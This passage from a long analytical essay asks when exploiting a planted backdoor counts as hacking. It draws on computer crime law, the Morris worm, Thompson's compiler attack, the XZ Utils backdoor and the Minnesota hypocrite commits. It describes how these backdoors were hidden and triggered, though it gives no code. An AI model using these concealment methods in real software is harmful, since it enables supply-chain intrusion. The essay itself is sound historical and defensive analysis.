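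If disclosure is enough, a maker could put one sentence about a secret entrance on page 90 of the manual. Zdziarski guards against this to some extent, because he doesn't accept consent that someone was forced to give or can't withdraw. But a backdoor has to meet all three of his conditions, so an entrance for the government that the maker fully discloses isn't one, even if nobody can switch it off. He accepts this and calls such an entrance "much worse than a backdoor". He says it is a surveillance tool and the law should treat it as one. It would seem to follow that an agency using it isn't hacking, however much the owners object.

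Disclosure to the owner also doesn't reach everyone who relies on a system. Houseguests use the router without seeing its manual, and patients rely on a hospital's computers without being told anything about them. Zdziarski considers only the owner, which makes the test easier to apply but leaves out people who may have more to lose.

Even if the maker disclosed nothing, there may still be evidence of what users expected. Zdziarski says that a login mechanism explicitly sets a security boundary by controlling who gets in, and there would be little point in choosing a password if a stranger's phrase worked just as well. This settles the simple cases but is less helpful with File Relay, where users had to guess what a computer could read once they had paired a phone with it.

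The first view is similarly vague. Dullien notes that programmers often have no specification or a very incomplete one, so the designers' intentions may be no more definite than the users' expectations. The designers' intentions are also harder for an outsider to check, because companies publish their manuals but usually not their internal discussions.

A more serious difficulty for the second view is the owner who sends the D-Link string to his own router. He gets in by a route that D-Link never told him about, and so does a technician who uses a maintenance password because the owner asked for help. It would be odd to call either of them a hacker. A defender of the view can answer that the owner agreed in both cases, but then they are not hackers because they had the owner's permission, regardless of what anyone expected of the router.

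## The view that permission decides: computer crime law

The third view makes permission the test for everyone, whether a programmer created the way in by mistake or on purpose. Criminal law takes roughly this approach. Orin Kerr, a law professor and former federal prosecutor of computer crime, wrote in *Cybercrime's Scope* (2003) that the US federal government, all fifty states and more than forty other countries had laws against unauthorized access to computers. He complained that no one seemed to know what these laws covered. A conviction under these laws doesn't prove that the act was hacking in the ordinary sense. But courts have had to decide who can permit what, which the other two views mostly leave open.

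### The offence of unauthorized access

The main US statute is the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act of 1986, or CFAA. Its core offence covers anyone who "intentionally accesses a computer without authorization or exceeds authorized access" and thereby obtains information, as quoted in the law firm Gibson Dunn's case note *Van Buren v. United States* (2021). The Act does not define authorization, but it defines exceeding authorized access as using a computer with permission and then getting or altering information in it that one is "not entitled" to get or alter. In his *Brief of Professor Orin S. Kerr as Amicus Curiae* (2020) to the Supreme Court, Kerr objected that this definition is circular, since "entitled" is only another word for "authorized".

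The other parts of the offence exclude very little. The Act protects any computer used in or affecting interstate or foreign commerce, according to Patent Docs' *Van Buren v. United States* (2021), and Kerr argued that this covers practically everything with a microchip. Merely viewing information counts as obtaining it. An outsider who sent the D-Link string and looked at the router's settings would therefore have met every condition except, possibly, the lack of authorization, and how the vulnerability got into the router isn't one of the conditions.

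The CFAA also makes it a separate offence to knowingly send a program, code or command and so intentionally cause damage without authorization. Under the Act, "damage" means harming the integrity of a system, a program or the data it holds, or making any of them less available. This offence matters for people who plant vulnerabilities because they are often authorized to access the computer they are changing.

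Britain's Computer Misuse Act 1990 is clearer about permission. A person commits its basic offence if he makes a computer perform any function, intending to get access to a program or data, and knows the access is unauthorized. He doesn't have to succeed. Access is unauthorized if he is not entitled to control access of that kind and does not have consent from someone who is.

The Budapest Convention of 2001, the first international treaty on cybercrime, requires its members to criminalize intentional access to all or part of a computer system "without right". Members may limit the crime to access gained by infringing security measures. In a country that has done so, someone who logged in with a backdoor phrase might argue that he infringed no security measure, because the login program accepted the phrase. The owner could reply that the password was the security measure and the phrase bypassed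 it.

### Who can give permission

The authority to permit use of a router could belong to its owner or to the company that designed its software. Kerr presumes that the owner or operator has the main authority, as a landowner does under the law of trespass. He adds that owners are always authorized to use their own computers under these statutes. The British wording leads to a similar answer, since a router's designer doesn't normally control who may use it after it is sold.

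In *Norms of Computer Trespass* (2016), Kerr uses keys to explain why permission decides. The owner of a house decides who gets a key and who may use it. A person who finds a lost key in the street can open the door but has no permission to, because the owner never authorized him, directly or through someone else. Only a locksmith hired by the owner may pick the lock. On this reasoning, a company that hires people to test its security has authorized them, while a programmer who builds a secret phrase into a router is like a builder who keeps a copy of the key to every house he sells.

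The maker might argue that the buyer agreed to the access by accepting the terms of sale. According to Kerr's discussion of consent in criminal law, courts generally ask whether the victim agreed to the act that took place, even if a lie about something else led the victim to agree. A man who borrows a car for a few minutes and keeps it for hours has not taken it without consent, because the owner agreed to let him drive it. But someone who buys a router and has never heard of the secret phrase hasn't agreed to let anyone use it. The maker would have a much better case if the terms described the maintenance entrance.

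Asking whether the owner gave permission works less well when the owner planted the vulnerability. Suppose a company runs an email service on its own machines and builds in a secret way to read its customers' messages. The company controls access to those machines, so its access is hard to call unauthorized, although other laws may forbid reading the messages. Customers who thought their passwords kept everyone else out would still feel that someone had broken into their accounts. Here the permission view seems to give a worse answer than the expectations view.

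An employee who plants a backdoor is in a weaker position than the company, because the authority to grant access belongs to the employer. Kerr cites *United States v. Steele*, a 2014 case in which a former employee kept using a backdoor account his old employer had failed to shut down. A federal appeals court held that this violated the CFAA. His permission had ended with his job, even though the account still worked.

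### Morris and the intended function of sendmail

The earliest important ruling on authorization, the Second Circuit's *United States v. Morris* (1991), did refer to what the software was for. Robert Tappan Morris was a Cornell graduate student who wanted to show how weak security was on the early internet. On 2 November 1988 he released a worm, a program that copies itself from one computer to the next. He designed it to check whether each computer already had a copy. Programmers could have blocked the worm by making their computers always answer yes, so Morris had it copy itself anyway every seventh time it got that answer. He badly underestimated how often computers would be asked, and machines around the country crashed or froze. Dealing with the worm cost each site from $200 to more than $53,000.

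The worm had four ways to get in:

- a hole in sendmail, a program that transfers email between computers;
- a hole in the finger program, which gives out limited information about a computer's users;
- the "trusted hosts" feature, which lets a user with privileges on one computer use another without a password;
- guessing passwords.

A jury convicted Morris, and the judge gave him three years of probation, 400 hours of community service and a fine of $10,050. The offence then required access "without authorization". Morris argued on appeal that he had at most exceeded his authorization, because he was allowed to use computers at Cornell, Harvard and Berkeley and could therefore send mail and finger requests to other computers on the network.

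The appeals court rejected this. It held that Morris had not used the mail and finger programs "in any way related to their intended function". He had found holes in them that gave him "a special and unauthorized access route into other computers", rather than using them to send mail or look up users. Kerr named this the intended function test. He thinks it rests on a general understanding among computer users that people who run a computer implicitly let others use its programs for the tasks the programs were designed for, but don't let them exploit weaknesses to do something else.

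The court described the sendmail hole as a bug, "an error", but the worm used a command called DEBUG, which was meant to help administrators find out why mail was going astray. With DEBUG on, a sender could put a list of commands in place of the recipient's address, and the receiving computer would run them.

Eric Allman, who wrote sendmail at Berkeley in the early 1980s, said in *Interview with Eric Allman* (Farrow, 2017) that he had put exactly one backdoor into the program. Someone had copied sendmail to a machine that Allman wasn't allowed to use, and its owners insisted that he fix a fault that appeared only there. They refused to let him log in, even with somebody watching. He gave them a new version containing a backdoor, which he used to fix the fault. He then left the backdoor in because it was convenient, and more or less forgot about it. He said of DEBUG, "Someone else put that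 into sendmail." He had answered "Are you nuts?" when somebody tried to get him to include it in the version he distributed.

Douglas McIlroy, a veteran of Unix, the operating system sendmail ran on, wrote in a mailing list message titled *Cool talk on Unix and Sendmail history, by Eric Allman* (2023) that the worm exploited "the unpardonable back door that Allman built into sendmail". Both men say Allman added the backdoor to help with a flood of trouble reports, but Allman says the worm didn't use it.

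A third account, from the month of the worm, comes from Carl Gutekunst, who maintained sendmail for the computer maker Pyramid. In *Internet Virus*, Gutekunst (1988) defended DEBUG as extremely useful to administrators and said the problem was the security holes in it. He had looked at it years before, decided it was "more useful than hazardous" and left it in, without noticing that it let any user send mail to a program to be run. He was replying to an exchange in which one person accused vendors of switching DEBUG on and another answered that Berkeley's own release came with it on. Gutekunst doesn't say who wrote DEBUG.

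### A hole built to let people in

If McIlroy is right, the intended function test has a problem. A backdoor's function is to let in people who don't have an account. Morris used the one in sendmail to get into computers where he had no account, so he arguably used it for its intended function. The same problem would arise under Allman's version of events if Morris had used the maintenance backdoor instead of DEBUG.

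One response is to describe the backdoor's function more fully. Allman says he built his to repair one installation, so its function did not include letting a student's worm into thousands of others. This approach rules out use by strangers, but not by the people a backdoor was planted for. If an intelligence service pays a company to build in a backdoor, the service's agents are using it for its intended function.

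Kerr's reading of the test works better. He points out that many people contributed to sendmail, so it had no particular designer whose intentions a court could consult. He concludes that the intended function must be the one claimed in the program and its supporting literature. An undocumented backdoor is not part of that function, whatever its planter wanted. McIlroy draws a similar line when he compares sendmail with uucp, another Unix program for communication between computers. The author of uucp refused to remove a feature that let one computer run commands on another. McIlroy thought it irresponsible to distribute the feature, but it was at least in the manual, and anyone who disliked it could delete or fix it. Allman's backdoor was visible in the code but undocumented. On Kerr's reading, however, the test no longer depends on designers and becomes a version of the view that users'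 expectations decide.

The court also had reasons that didn't depend on whether Morris used features as intended. The worm was designed to spread to computers where he had "no account and no authority, express or implied". The court also counted his use of trusted hosts and his guessing of passwords against him, although computers are designed to admit users from hosts they trust, and login programs are designed to admit anyone who types the right password. If using a feature as its designers intended had been a defence, these two routes would have been lawful. So *Morris* gives little support to someone who exploits a planted vulnerability and argues that it worked as planned.

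### Kerr's two tests

Kerr's own proposals concern what kind of barrier a person must get past to commit the crime. In 2003 he distinguished limits that a computer's owner sets by code, such as a password, from limits set by contract, such as terms of use. He compared the first to locking a door and the second to putting up a sign in front of an open one. He wanted only circumventing limits set by code to count as unauthorized access. Otherwise a website could announce that left-handed people may not visit, and any who did would be criminals.

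A user can circumvent code by posing as somebody else, as with a stolen password, or by exploiting a weakness that makes the program malfunction. For Kerr, the second method violates the intended function test. His example is a buffer overflow, so a stranger who exploits a bugdoor clearly violates the test too. An openly coded backdoor is harder to classify because nothing malfunctions. A person who types the secret phrase is arguably posing as the legitimate user, but a technician who uses an entrance built for technicians isn't posing as anyone.

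By 2016 Kerr had decided that this formulation was vague, because it was hard to tell when someone had circumvented a restriction in code. He replaced it with a test based on authentication, the step at which a computer checks who the user is. Under this test, access is unauthorized if the owner requires authentication and the person who gets in is neither the authenticated user nor that user's agent. The technician's access is unauthorized, even though the router's maker gave him a phrase that also works, because the owner required a password and never gave him one.

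The D-Link exploit consisted of changing the User-Agent text, and Kerr says in a footnote that getting around a restriction based on that text isn't trespass. Websites are open to everybody by default, and he regards such restrictions as speed bumps, like a newspaper's limit on free articles that a reader can avoid by deleting cookies. But he treats cookies that keep a user logged in differently. Such a cookie contains a long number that the site gives the browser after a login. Someone who intercepts that number and sends it to the site has trespassed, because it works as a temporary password. The D-Link string is like this second kind of cookie, since sending it gets the sender past a login that the owner relied on. Kerr accepts that the technology can't settle such questions and that the answers have to come from people's shared understanding of what is private.

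He also rereads *Morris* in these terms. The worm, he writes, got in "through a bug, not a feature", much as a burglar uses a window instead of the front door. A planted vulnerability is hard to classify this way, because it is a feature to the planter but looks like a bug to the owner. The comparison with a house still helps. If a builder puts a concealed door into a house and doesn't tell the buyer, few would think that the builder may use it, even though the door was made for people to walk through.

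### Gates that are up or down

The Supreme Court interpreted the CFAA's rules on authorization in *Van Buren v. United States* (2021). Nathan Van Buren, a police sergeant, had searched a government database for personal reasons, although he had been told to use it only for work. The Court ruled 6–3 in his favor. According to the Congressional Research Service's summary of the decision, the government's interpretation would have let restrictions in any statute or private agreement define the crime.

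Kerr (2021), in *The Supreme Court Reins In the CFAA in Van Buren*, explains the Court's alternative, a "gates-up-or-down inquiry". A person "either can or cannot access a computer system", and the same goes for particular files, folders or databases inside it. Van Buren's login let him into the database, so the gate was up. A workplace rule about his reasons for using the database didn't change that.

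The Court didn't fully explain what a closed gate is. In one footnote it connected gates with authentication, which is Kerr's test, but in another it declined to decide whether contracts and policies can also close a gate. Schneier (2021), in *The Supreme Court Narrowed the CFAA*, welcomed the ruling but thought the second footnote made no sense, since the Court had just cleared a man who had only broken a policy. Kerr was also puzzled, and concluded that the Court had left lower courts to work out which barriers count.

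Nobody thinks the Court meant to allow a thief to get into an account with a stolen password, so its phrase "can or cannot" shouldn't be read literally. A literal reading would protect anyone who is able to get in, including anyone who uses a backdoor, such as a stranger who knows the D-Link string. Kerr paraphrases the crime as bypassing a closed gate that one isn't supposed to bypass. The owner, who set the password, is the obvious person to say who is supposed to get through.

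The table below shows roughly how computer crime law treats each person involved in a planted vulnerability. It assumes that the planter works on the software as part of his job and that the computer's owner does not know about the backdoor.

| Person | Kerr's code test (2003) | Kerr's authentication test (2016) | *Van Buren* gates |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planter writing the backdoor at work | Authorized, though he may break a company rule | Authorized: he logs in as himself | Gate up |
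| Person the backdoor was meant for | Unclear: nothing malfunctions and he may not be posing as anyone | Unauthorized: the owner never admitted him | Probably down |
| Stranger who finds it | Probably unauthorized: he passes for a legitimate user | Unauthorized | Down |
| Anyone the owner has asked to use it | Authorized | Authorized | Gate up |

The planter fares best under these tests, which may seem unfair. The tests are about entering a computer, and his employer had already let him in. If he later used the backdoor to reach files that were closed to him, or to get back in after leaving the company, he would be in the same position as a stranger.

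British courts have given more weight to what an employer allowed. In 1999 the House of Lords, then the country's highest court, considered an American Express employee whose job covered only the customer accounts assigned to her, but who opened others that the computer let her access. The Lords held that this could be unauthorized access. Under the *Van Buren* test, her lawyers could have argued that her access was authorized because the computer let her open those accounts.

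A broad idea of permission, however, would class too much behaviour as hacking. Kerr describes a survey in which the legal scholar Matthew Kugler asked 593 American adults to rate, from one to six, how far various computer users were authorized to do what they did. The highest average score, only 2.32, went to an employee who checked the weather on a work computer for personal reasons. Yet 60 per cent thought he should not be punished, and another 32 per cent would have given him the equivalent of a parking ticket. People evidently consider much behaviour unauthorized that they wouldn't call hacking. To match ordinary usage, the permission view must require something like Kerr's gate as well as a lack of permission.

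### Machines that pay out

Gambling machines are a useful comparison because anyone may play them, usually without a login. In a 2013 blog post about computer crime and casinos, which Kerr quotes, the legal scholar James Grimmelmann summed up the defence available in any CFAA case: "You say I shouldn't have done it, but the computer said I could!"

In 2009 John Kane discovered a fault in a widely used model of video poker machine. If the Double Up option was on, a player could win a hand at a low stake, make a certain series of changes between games, and get the machine to pay the same hand again at a much higher stake. The manufacturer had not intended this. Kane and Andre Nestor used the fault to win several hundred thousand dollars, pressing only the buttons on the machines. Federal prosecutors charged them under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act and with conspiracy to commit wire fraud.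 Prosecutors dropped the computer charge in 2013 and the fraud charge later that year.

This was plainly a hack in Schneier's sense. The CFAA fits it poorly, because the men were allowed to play and did not bypass any access barrier. Kerr's 2003 test might have covered their conduct, since they exploited a weakness in the program, but his 2016 test probably would not.

Ron Harris and Eddie Tipton exploited flaws that they had planted themselves. Harris worked for the Nevada Gaming Control Board, which inspects slot machines. In the early 1990s he altered the board's inspection software so that checking a machine also installed his code on it. The code made the machine pay out when a player inserted coins in a particular sequence. The authorities caught him in 1995 after an accomplice won $100,000 at keno in Atlantic City. Harris had worked out how the keno game generated its numbers, so that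 win didn't involve planted code. He pleaded guilty to cheating charges in Nevada, and a judge sentenced him to seven years in prison.

Tipton headed information security at the Multi-State Lottery Association, which ran draws for lotteries in many US states. He added code to the program that picked winning numbers so that he could predict its output on a few dates each year, if certain other conditions held. In December 2010 he bought a ticket in Iowa worth 16.5 million dollars, and friends and relatives collected prizes in other states. An Iowa jury convicted him of fraud in 2015, though the state's supreme court later overturned part of the verdict. In 2017 he pleaded guilty in Iowa to ongoing criminal conduct and received a sentence of up to 25 years. He also pleaded guilty that year in Wisconsin to theft by fraud and a computer crime.

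The outcomes suggest that a person can do wrong even by using a flaw as its planter intended. The men who exploited flaws they had planted went to prison, while Kane and Nestor, who exploited an accidental one, went free. But three cases from different courts are too few to establish a rule, and prosecutors dropped the charges against Kane and Nestor before any appeals court ruled on them. The planters had also betrayed employers who trusted them to keep the games honest, so there was fraud whether or not anyone had hacked a machine.

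Permission to use the computer explains less here. Tipton's friends never touched the lottery's computer, because the exploit only required buying a ticket with the right numbers, which anyone may do. If a stranger had studied past draws, noticed the pattern and bet on it, he would have used the same planted vulnerability but looked much more like Kane than like Tipton.

### Davis Lu

The conviction of Davis Lu in March 2025 shows that US law can punish someone for planting harmful code even if he needed no exploit to get in. Lu, a software developer, had worked since 2007 for a company headquartered in Ohio. After a reorganization in 2018 reduced his responsibilities, he began to sabotage its systems. Some of his code ran in endless loops until the servers crashed. He also wrote a kill switch that checked whether his account was still active in the company's user directory and locked everyone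 out if it wasn't. He named it "IsDLEnabledinAD", short for "Is Davis Lu enabled in Active Directory".

The company put him on leave in September 2019 and disabled his account. This triggered the switch, and thousands of employees around the world couldn't log in. A federal jury found him guilty of intentionally damaging protected computers, and in August 2025 a judge sentenced him to four years in prison.

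Prosecutors relied on the damage offence and not on unauthorized access. This fits *Van Buren*, because Lu's job gave him authorized access to the company's systems. Kerr had argued in 2003 that such cases belong under a damage law. He discussed a programmer who had deleted his employer's files, and said the man's real crime was destroying them, not getting into the computer. He also noted that "without authorization" has a different sense in the damage offence, where it means that nobody permitted the damage. Lu's employer had allowed him to change its software, but not to make it lock out the staff.

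Lu's kill switch gave nobody access, so it was not a backdoor. If he had instead planted a secret login phrase and never used it, the company's systems would have kept running normally. The statute's definition of damage includes impairment to the "integrity" of a system, and a prosecutor could argue that a login program that admits strangers has lost its integrity. Lu's jury didn't have to consider that argument, because his code had stopped thousands of people from working.

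## Whether the product or the process that made it is subverted

Davis Lu sabotaged software that his employer had allowed him to change. Schneier holds that a programmer with such permission who adds a backdoor has hacked the software development process, not the code. The process here means everything between a programmer's idea and the software on somebody's computer, including the people who are allowed to change the code, the people who review the changes, the tools that translate the code into a form a computer can run, and whoever packages the result for release.

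In the same essay, Schneier writes that "hacking is not cheating", because a hacker follows a system's rules while subverting their intent. If he is right about backdoors, the people who planted them followed the rules of the process that made the program, and nobody hacked the finished program itself. A few cases are documented well enough to test this.

### A compiler that alters what it compiles

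Programmers write source code, which people can read. A program called a compiler translates it into a binary, the instructions that a processor runs. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, explained in his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (1984), how a compiler could put a backdoor into another program. He started with two harmless tricks and built up to the backdoor from them.

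One is the old student puzzle of writing a program that outputs an exact copy of its own source code. Such programs exist, and they can contain any amount of extra text, which they also copy.

The other trick depends on the C compiler being a C program, so programmers use the existing compiler to make the next one. C has short codes for characters that don't print, such as `\n` for a new line. Suppose the programmers want to add `\v` for a vertical tab, which is character number 11. The existing compiler rejects `\v`, so they first write the number 11 into the compiler's source and compile that. The new binary handles `\v` correctly. They can then replace the 11 in the source with `\v`, and the compiler still works. The number that `\v` stands for is no longer in the source, but it is in the binary and in every compiler made with that binary.

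Thompson used the same self-copying trick to hide a backdoor. He made two alterations to the compiler. The first recognizes the source code of the Unix login program and compiles it so that it accepts either the user's real password or one that Thompson knows. Anybody who read the compiler's source would soon notice this, so the second recognizes the source code of the compiler itself and puts both alterations into the new binary. Thompson compiled the altered source once, installed the result as the official compiler, and could then delete both alterations from the source.

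| What someone compiles | Compiler they use | What they get |
|---|---|---|
| Compiler source with both alterations | Clean compiler | Altered compiler |
| Clean compiler source | Altered compiler | Altered compiler |
| Clean login source | Altered compiler | Login program with a backdoor |

Only the first row involves suspicious source code, and Thompson needed that code only once. Afterwards a reviewer could read every line of the login program and the compiler without finding the backdoor, because it is only in the binaries. Recompiling doesn't remove it, since the altered compiler puts it back. Thompson concluded that nobody can trust code they did not totally create themselves. His example was a compiler, but he said that any program that handles other programs could hide a backdoor the same way, and that flaws at lower levels, such as a processor's microcode, would be even harder to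 find.

The idea wasn't entirely his. He credited an Air Force critique of Multics that he could no longer locate, evidently Karger and Schell's.

Accounts differ on what happened when Thompson tried out his compiler backdoor. According to *Countering "Trusting Trust"* (2006), a post on Schneier's blog, the people whose compiler he had altered never noticed, even when they examined the binaries, because the compiler had also rigged the tool they used. According to *Trusting Trust*, a page of personal notes, somebody in another department saw that the compiler grew by one byte every time it compiled itself, and accidentally removed the backdoor by rebuilding the compiler from lower-level code. The notes rely on forum posts and are weak evidence, but a small bug like that is a believable way for such a scheme to fail.

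Schneier's claim works well for the login program. Thompson never touched its source, and whoever maintained it had done nothing wrong, so the fault lay entirely in the process. But the compiler is also a product, which people install and rely on like any other program. Thompson subverted the login program's process by altering the compiler's code. Whether a planter has subverted a product or a process can therefore depend on which program one asks about.

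### Checking with a second compiler

For about two decades, people who knew of Thompson's lecture generally thought there was no defence against the attack it described. David Wheeler, of the Institute for Defense Analyses, recalls on his page about the attack that he wondered whether anyone should use computers if that was true. In *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2005), he proposed a test that uses a second compiler from a different source.

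Call the compiler's published source code *s*, the suspect binary *A*, and the second compiler *T*. Write *T*(*s*) for the binary that *T* produces from *s*. The test has three steps:

1. Compile the source with the second compiler: *B*₁ = *T*(*s*).
2. Compile the same source again with the result: *B*₂ = *B*₁(*s*).
3. Compare *B*₂ with *A*, bit by bit.

*B*₁'s instructions will differ from *A*'s, because different compilers translate the same source differently. But *B*₁ and an honest *A* are both translations of *s*, so they should behave the same on the same input. If an honest *A* reproduces itself when it compiles *s*, *B*₁ should also produce an identical copy of *A*. If *A* contains Thompson's alterations, *B*₂ will differ from it, since neither *T* nor *s* supplied them. Wheeler wrote in his abstract, which van Wyk (2005) quoted on a secure programming mailing list, that if *A* and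 *B*₂ match, the source "accurately represents the binary".

This depends on several assumptions. *T* must be able to compile *s* correctly and must not contain the same alterations. It can be slow and produce inefficient code, because *B*₁ only has to behave correctly. It could have a backdoor, as long as the backdoor does nothing when *T* compiles *s*. Compiling the same input must always produce the same bits, and the tester must have the exact source and settings that produced *A*. The computer that makes the comparison must also be free of tampering. In Schneier's version of the Thompson story, the tools for inspecting binaries had been subverted too.

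A mismatch doesn't prove that anyone planted anything. Wheeler says the method also finds some ordinary compiler defects. A match shows only that the binary corresponds to its source. Somebody still has to read the source, because the test can't show whether the people who wrote it were honest. Their honesty was the weak point in the best-documented backdoor since Thompson's.

### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

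Most versions of Linux include XZ Utils, a set of free programs for compressing files. It is open source, so anyone can read the code and propose changes, called patches. A maintainer decides which patches to accept, and for years the only maintainer was a volunteer, Lasse Collin.

*Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024), by the programmer Russ Cox, reconstructs what happened. On 29 October 2021 somebody using the name Jia Tan sent the project's mailing list a small, harmless patch. More patches followed, and they look fine in retrospect. From April 2022 someone called Jigar Kumar complained on the list that Tan's patches were taking too long. In May someone called Dennis Ens asked whether another part of the project still had a maintainer. Collin apologized for being slow. He explained in June that long-term mental health issues had limited what he could do, and that XZ was "an unpaid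 hobby project". Ens replied that he was sorry to hear it, but that "the community desires more" and Collin should consider handing over part of the work.

On 29 June Collin wrote that Tan was "practically a co-maintainer already". By the end of the year Tan could put changes directly into the project. Kumar's and Ens's email addresses seem never to have appeared anywhere else, even in leaked data, and Cox thinks they were probably fakes made to push Collin into giving Tan more control. That inference is reasonable, though nobody has shown who sent the emails.

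Tan then did much of the ordinary work of running the project. In *Wolves in the Repository*, Przymus and Durieux (2025) examined 1,020 commits (recorded changes to the project's files), 2,944 events on the hosting site GitHub and 307 mailing list messages. Most of Tan's contributions were documentation and translation, which draw less scrutiny than code. Tan also reviewed other people's code reasonably well, answered questions and announced releases. Only eight commits were malicious, all in 2024. Przymus and Durieux point out that a maintainer has little chance of telling such a person from an enthusiastic volunteer, and that treating every volunteer with suspicion would drive away the help small projects need.

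### A release that differed from the public source

The backdoor came in two pieces. On 23 February 2024 Tan added some test files to the repository, the public store of the project's source. Developers test a compression program on odd and damaged files, which aren't readable text. According to project notes written long before Tan arrived, many of the test files were made by hand and had no better source than the files themselves. Most of the backdoor was inside two of the files Tan added, where it did nothing.

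The next day Tan published version 5.6.0 as a release package, the archive from which Linux distributions such as Debian build their own copies. Tan had modified the package's build script, which turns the source into a binary, so that it extracted the backdoor from the test files and added it to XZ's compression library. The modified script wasn't in the repository, but that wasn't suspicious in itself, because release packages usually include a few generated files that the repository lacks. Anyone who reviewed the repository would have seen some strange test data and no code that used it.

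The script added the backdoor only on Linux machines with a common type of processor, and only when someone was building a package for Debian, Red Hat or related systems. An investigator who compiled XZ by hand would have got a clean copy.

Tan didn't need to forge anything to do this. Collin writes in Tukaani's *xz backdoor* (2024) that Tan created and signed the packages. A distribution that checked the signature would have correctly concluded that the package came from one of the project's maintainers. Collin also found no sign that Tan had forged other people's commits or rewritten the project's history.

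Unlike Thompson's compiler, this attack left evidence that a careful reader could find, because the altered script was readable text in a public package. But the backdoor was hidden from people who read only the repository. *Build Code is Still Code* (2026) attributes the attack to a lack of separation between build phases, and proposes running each phase in its own restricted environment so that a build script could not turn test data into part of the library.

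### A backdoor that needs a private key

Tan's target was OpenSSH, a program administrators use to log in to servers remotely. OpenSSH itself doesn't use XZ's library, but Debian and several other distributions had modified it to notify systemd, the program that starts and stops services on Linux. The modified version used systemd's library, which loaded XZ's. When an affected server started OpenSSH, the backdoor started too. It then intercepted calls to a function OpenSSH uses to check digital signatures during logins and redirected them to its own code.

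A digital signature needs a pair of keys. The owner signs a message with the private key, and others use the public key to check it, but they can't use the public key to sign. The planter put a public key into the backdoor and kept the private one. In a reply to the message that had announced the discovery, Patrakov (2024) passed on a preliminary analysis by the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda that explains what happens next:

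- Someone connects to the server and presents a key of their own, as some logins require. A command is hidden inside that key.
- The backdoor decrypts the command and checks whether the planter's private key signed it.
- If the signature is valid, the server runs the command, before anyone has logged in.
- If it isn't, the backdoor does nothing more and the ordinary login continues.

Anyone who read the D-Link router's program could learn the secret phrase and use it straight away, but someone who takes the XZ backdoor apart finds only the public key. Recording one of the planter's commands wouldn't help much, because the signature also covers the key that identifies the particular server, so the command would fail on other servers. Affected servers also respond normally to everyone but the planter, so nobody could write a reliable scanner to find them over the internet.

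Valsorda described the backdoor as a way to run commands, not to bypass the login. A later analysis on Securelist, the research site of the security company Kaspersky, found that it could do both. The backdoor let the holder of the key log in with any username and password, and kept those logins out of the server's records.

### Half a second

Andres Freund, a Microsoft developer who works on the database PostgreSQL, found the XZ backdoor by accident. Over several weeks he noticed that logins on a test version of Debian were using a lot of processor time, and that Valgrind, a tool for finding memory errors, was reporting problems in XZ's library. Freund (2024) reports in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* that a failed login took 0.8 seconds with the new version, up from 0.3 seconds. The delay came from the backdoor searching through the names of functions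 in memory for the one it was meant to redirect.

Freund first suspected that someone had tampered with Debian's copy, then found the same tampering in the original packages. He alerted Debian privately on 28 March 2024 and published his findings the next day, adding that he was not a security researcher.

Tan had already responded to Valgrind errors in early March by publishing a fake fix as a distraction and then replacing the two test files. Tan said that the originals contained random data and that files generated from a fixed starting value would be easier to reproduce. The new files contained a repaired backdoor, which went out in version 5.6.1 on 9 March. Tan may have been short of time, because systemd's developers had just accepted a change, apparently for unrelated reasons, that would have stopped their library from loading XZ's.

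Within days, distributions withdrew the affected versions, which had reached mostly test editions. Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used the backdoor. Collin reviewed each of Tan's commits and found nearly all of them acceptable, often after making small corrections. Besides the backdoor, he found a single stray full stop in a build file, which had silently disabled a check for Landlock, a Linux security feature that restricts what a program may do. He released a clean version on 29 May 2024.

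In August 2025 the security company Binarly found at least 35 ready-made Linux images on the download site Docker Hub that still contained the backdoor. Debian declined to remove its own images, saying they were old development builds of historical interest. Nobody has publicly established who Jia Tan was, or whether the name belonged to one person. Someone calling himself Hans Jansen supplied a feature in 2023 that the backdoor later needed, and reappeared in March 2024 to ask Debian to adopt version 5.6.1. Przymus and Durieux leave open whether his patches were a genuine improvement or part of the plan.

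### Breaking in and being let in

Other planters have broken into the servers that store or distribute software. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026), a paper on catching backdoors before release, describes several cases. In 2010 and 2011 attackers broke into the servers that distributed two file-transfer programs, ProFTPD and vsFTPd, and replaced the packages with backdoored ones. In the altered vsFTPd, typing a smiley, ":)", as the username opened a command line with full control of the computer. In 2021 attackers got into the server that held the source code of the programming language PHP and added a backdoor, which the developers found before any release.

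These planters ignored the rules of the development process. They hacked the computers it ran on, in the ordinary sense of the word, and changed the code without permission from anyone with authority over it. Collin had agreed to let Tan change the code, so better passwords or locked-down servers would not have stopped the XZ backdoor.

After XZ, some organizations began to trust contributors less. *S3C2 Summit 2025-03* (2025) describes a meeting of companies where one participant had a policy of assuming that any commit might be malicious, and others agreed. They also discussed Thompson's lecture and how hard it is to find anything to anchor trust to. According to *S3C2 Summit 2025-07* (2026), participants at a similar meeting for government agencies thought that users of commercial software have to trust the vendor, while users of open-source software trust the source code and the process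 that delivered it. In XZ, the public source looked harmless, but the process delivered software that did not match it.

### The Minnesota patches

Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota had already tried deceiving a project's reviewers as an experiment. Their paper, *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software via Hypocrite Commits* (2021), concerns the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system. Their method starts with code that meets some, but not all, of the conditions for a vulnerability. A short patch can fix a real, minor bug there while adding the missing condition. Wu and Lu concentrated on flaws in which a program keeps using memory after releasing it.

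In 2020 researchers emailed three flawed patches to Linux kernel maintainers under false names. If a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, they pointed out the flaw, asked him not to apply it, and offered a correct patch. They concluded that a malicious contributor could get such flaws accepted. The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board reviewed the case in May 2021 and disagreed, finding that maintainers had caught or ignored all of the invalid patches. Three patches are also too few to estimate how often review fails.

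Most of the anger came in April 2021, when another Minnesota researcher sent patches that maintainers thought were useless. He said they came from a new code analysis tool. Greg Kroah-Hartman, one of the kernel's senior maintainers, suspected another experiment. He stopped accepting contributions from the university and began removing its earlier ones until someone had rechecked them. Developers then spent weeks reviewing several hundred old patches, most of which were correct. The university suspended the research. Wu and Lu apologized and withdrew the paper, which a leading security conference had accepted. They said they should have consulted the kernel developers first and did not want their study to be a model for others.

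The university's ethics board had decided that the study was not research on human subjects. That makes sense on the narrow view that the researchers were testing code. The maintainers disagreed because the experiment consisted of lying to them and seeing whether they noticed. Unlike a company that hires people to test its security, they had not agreed to be tested.

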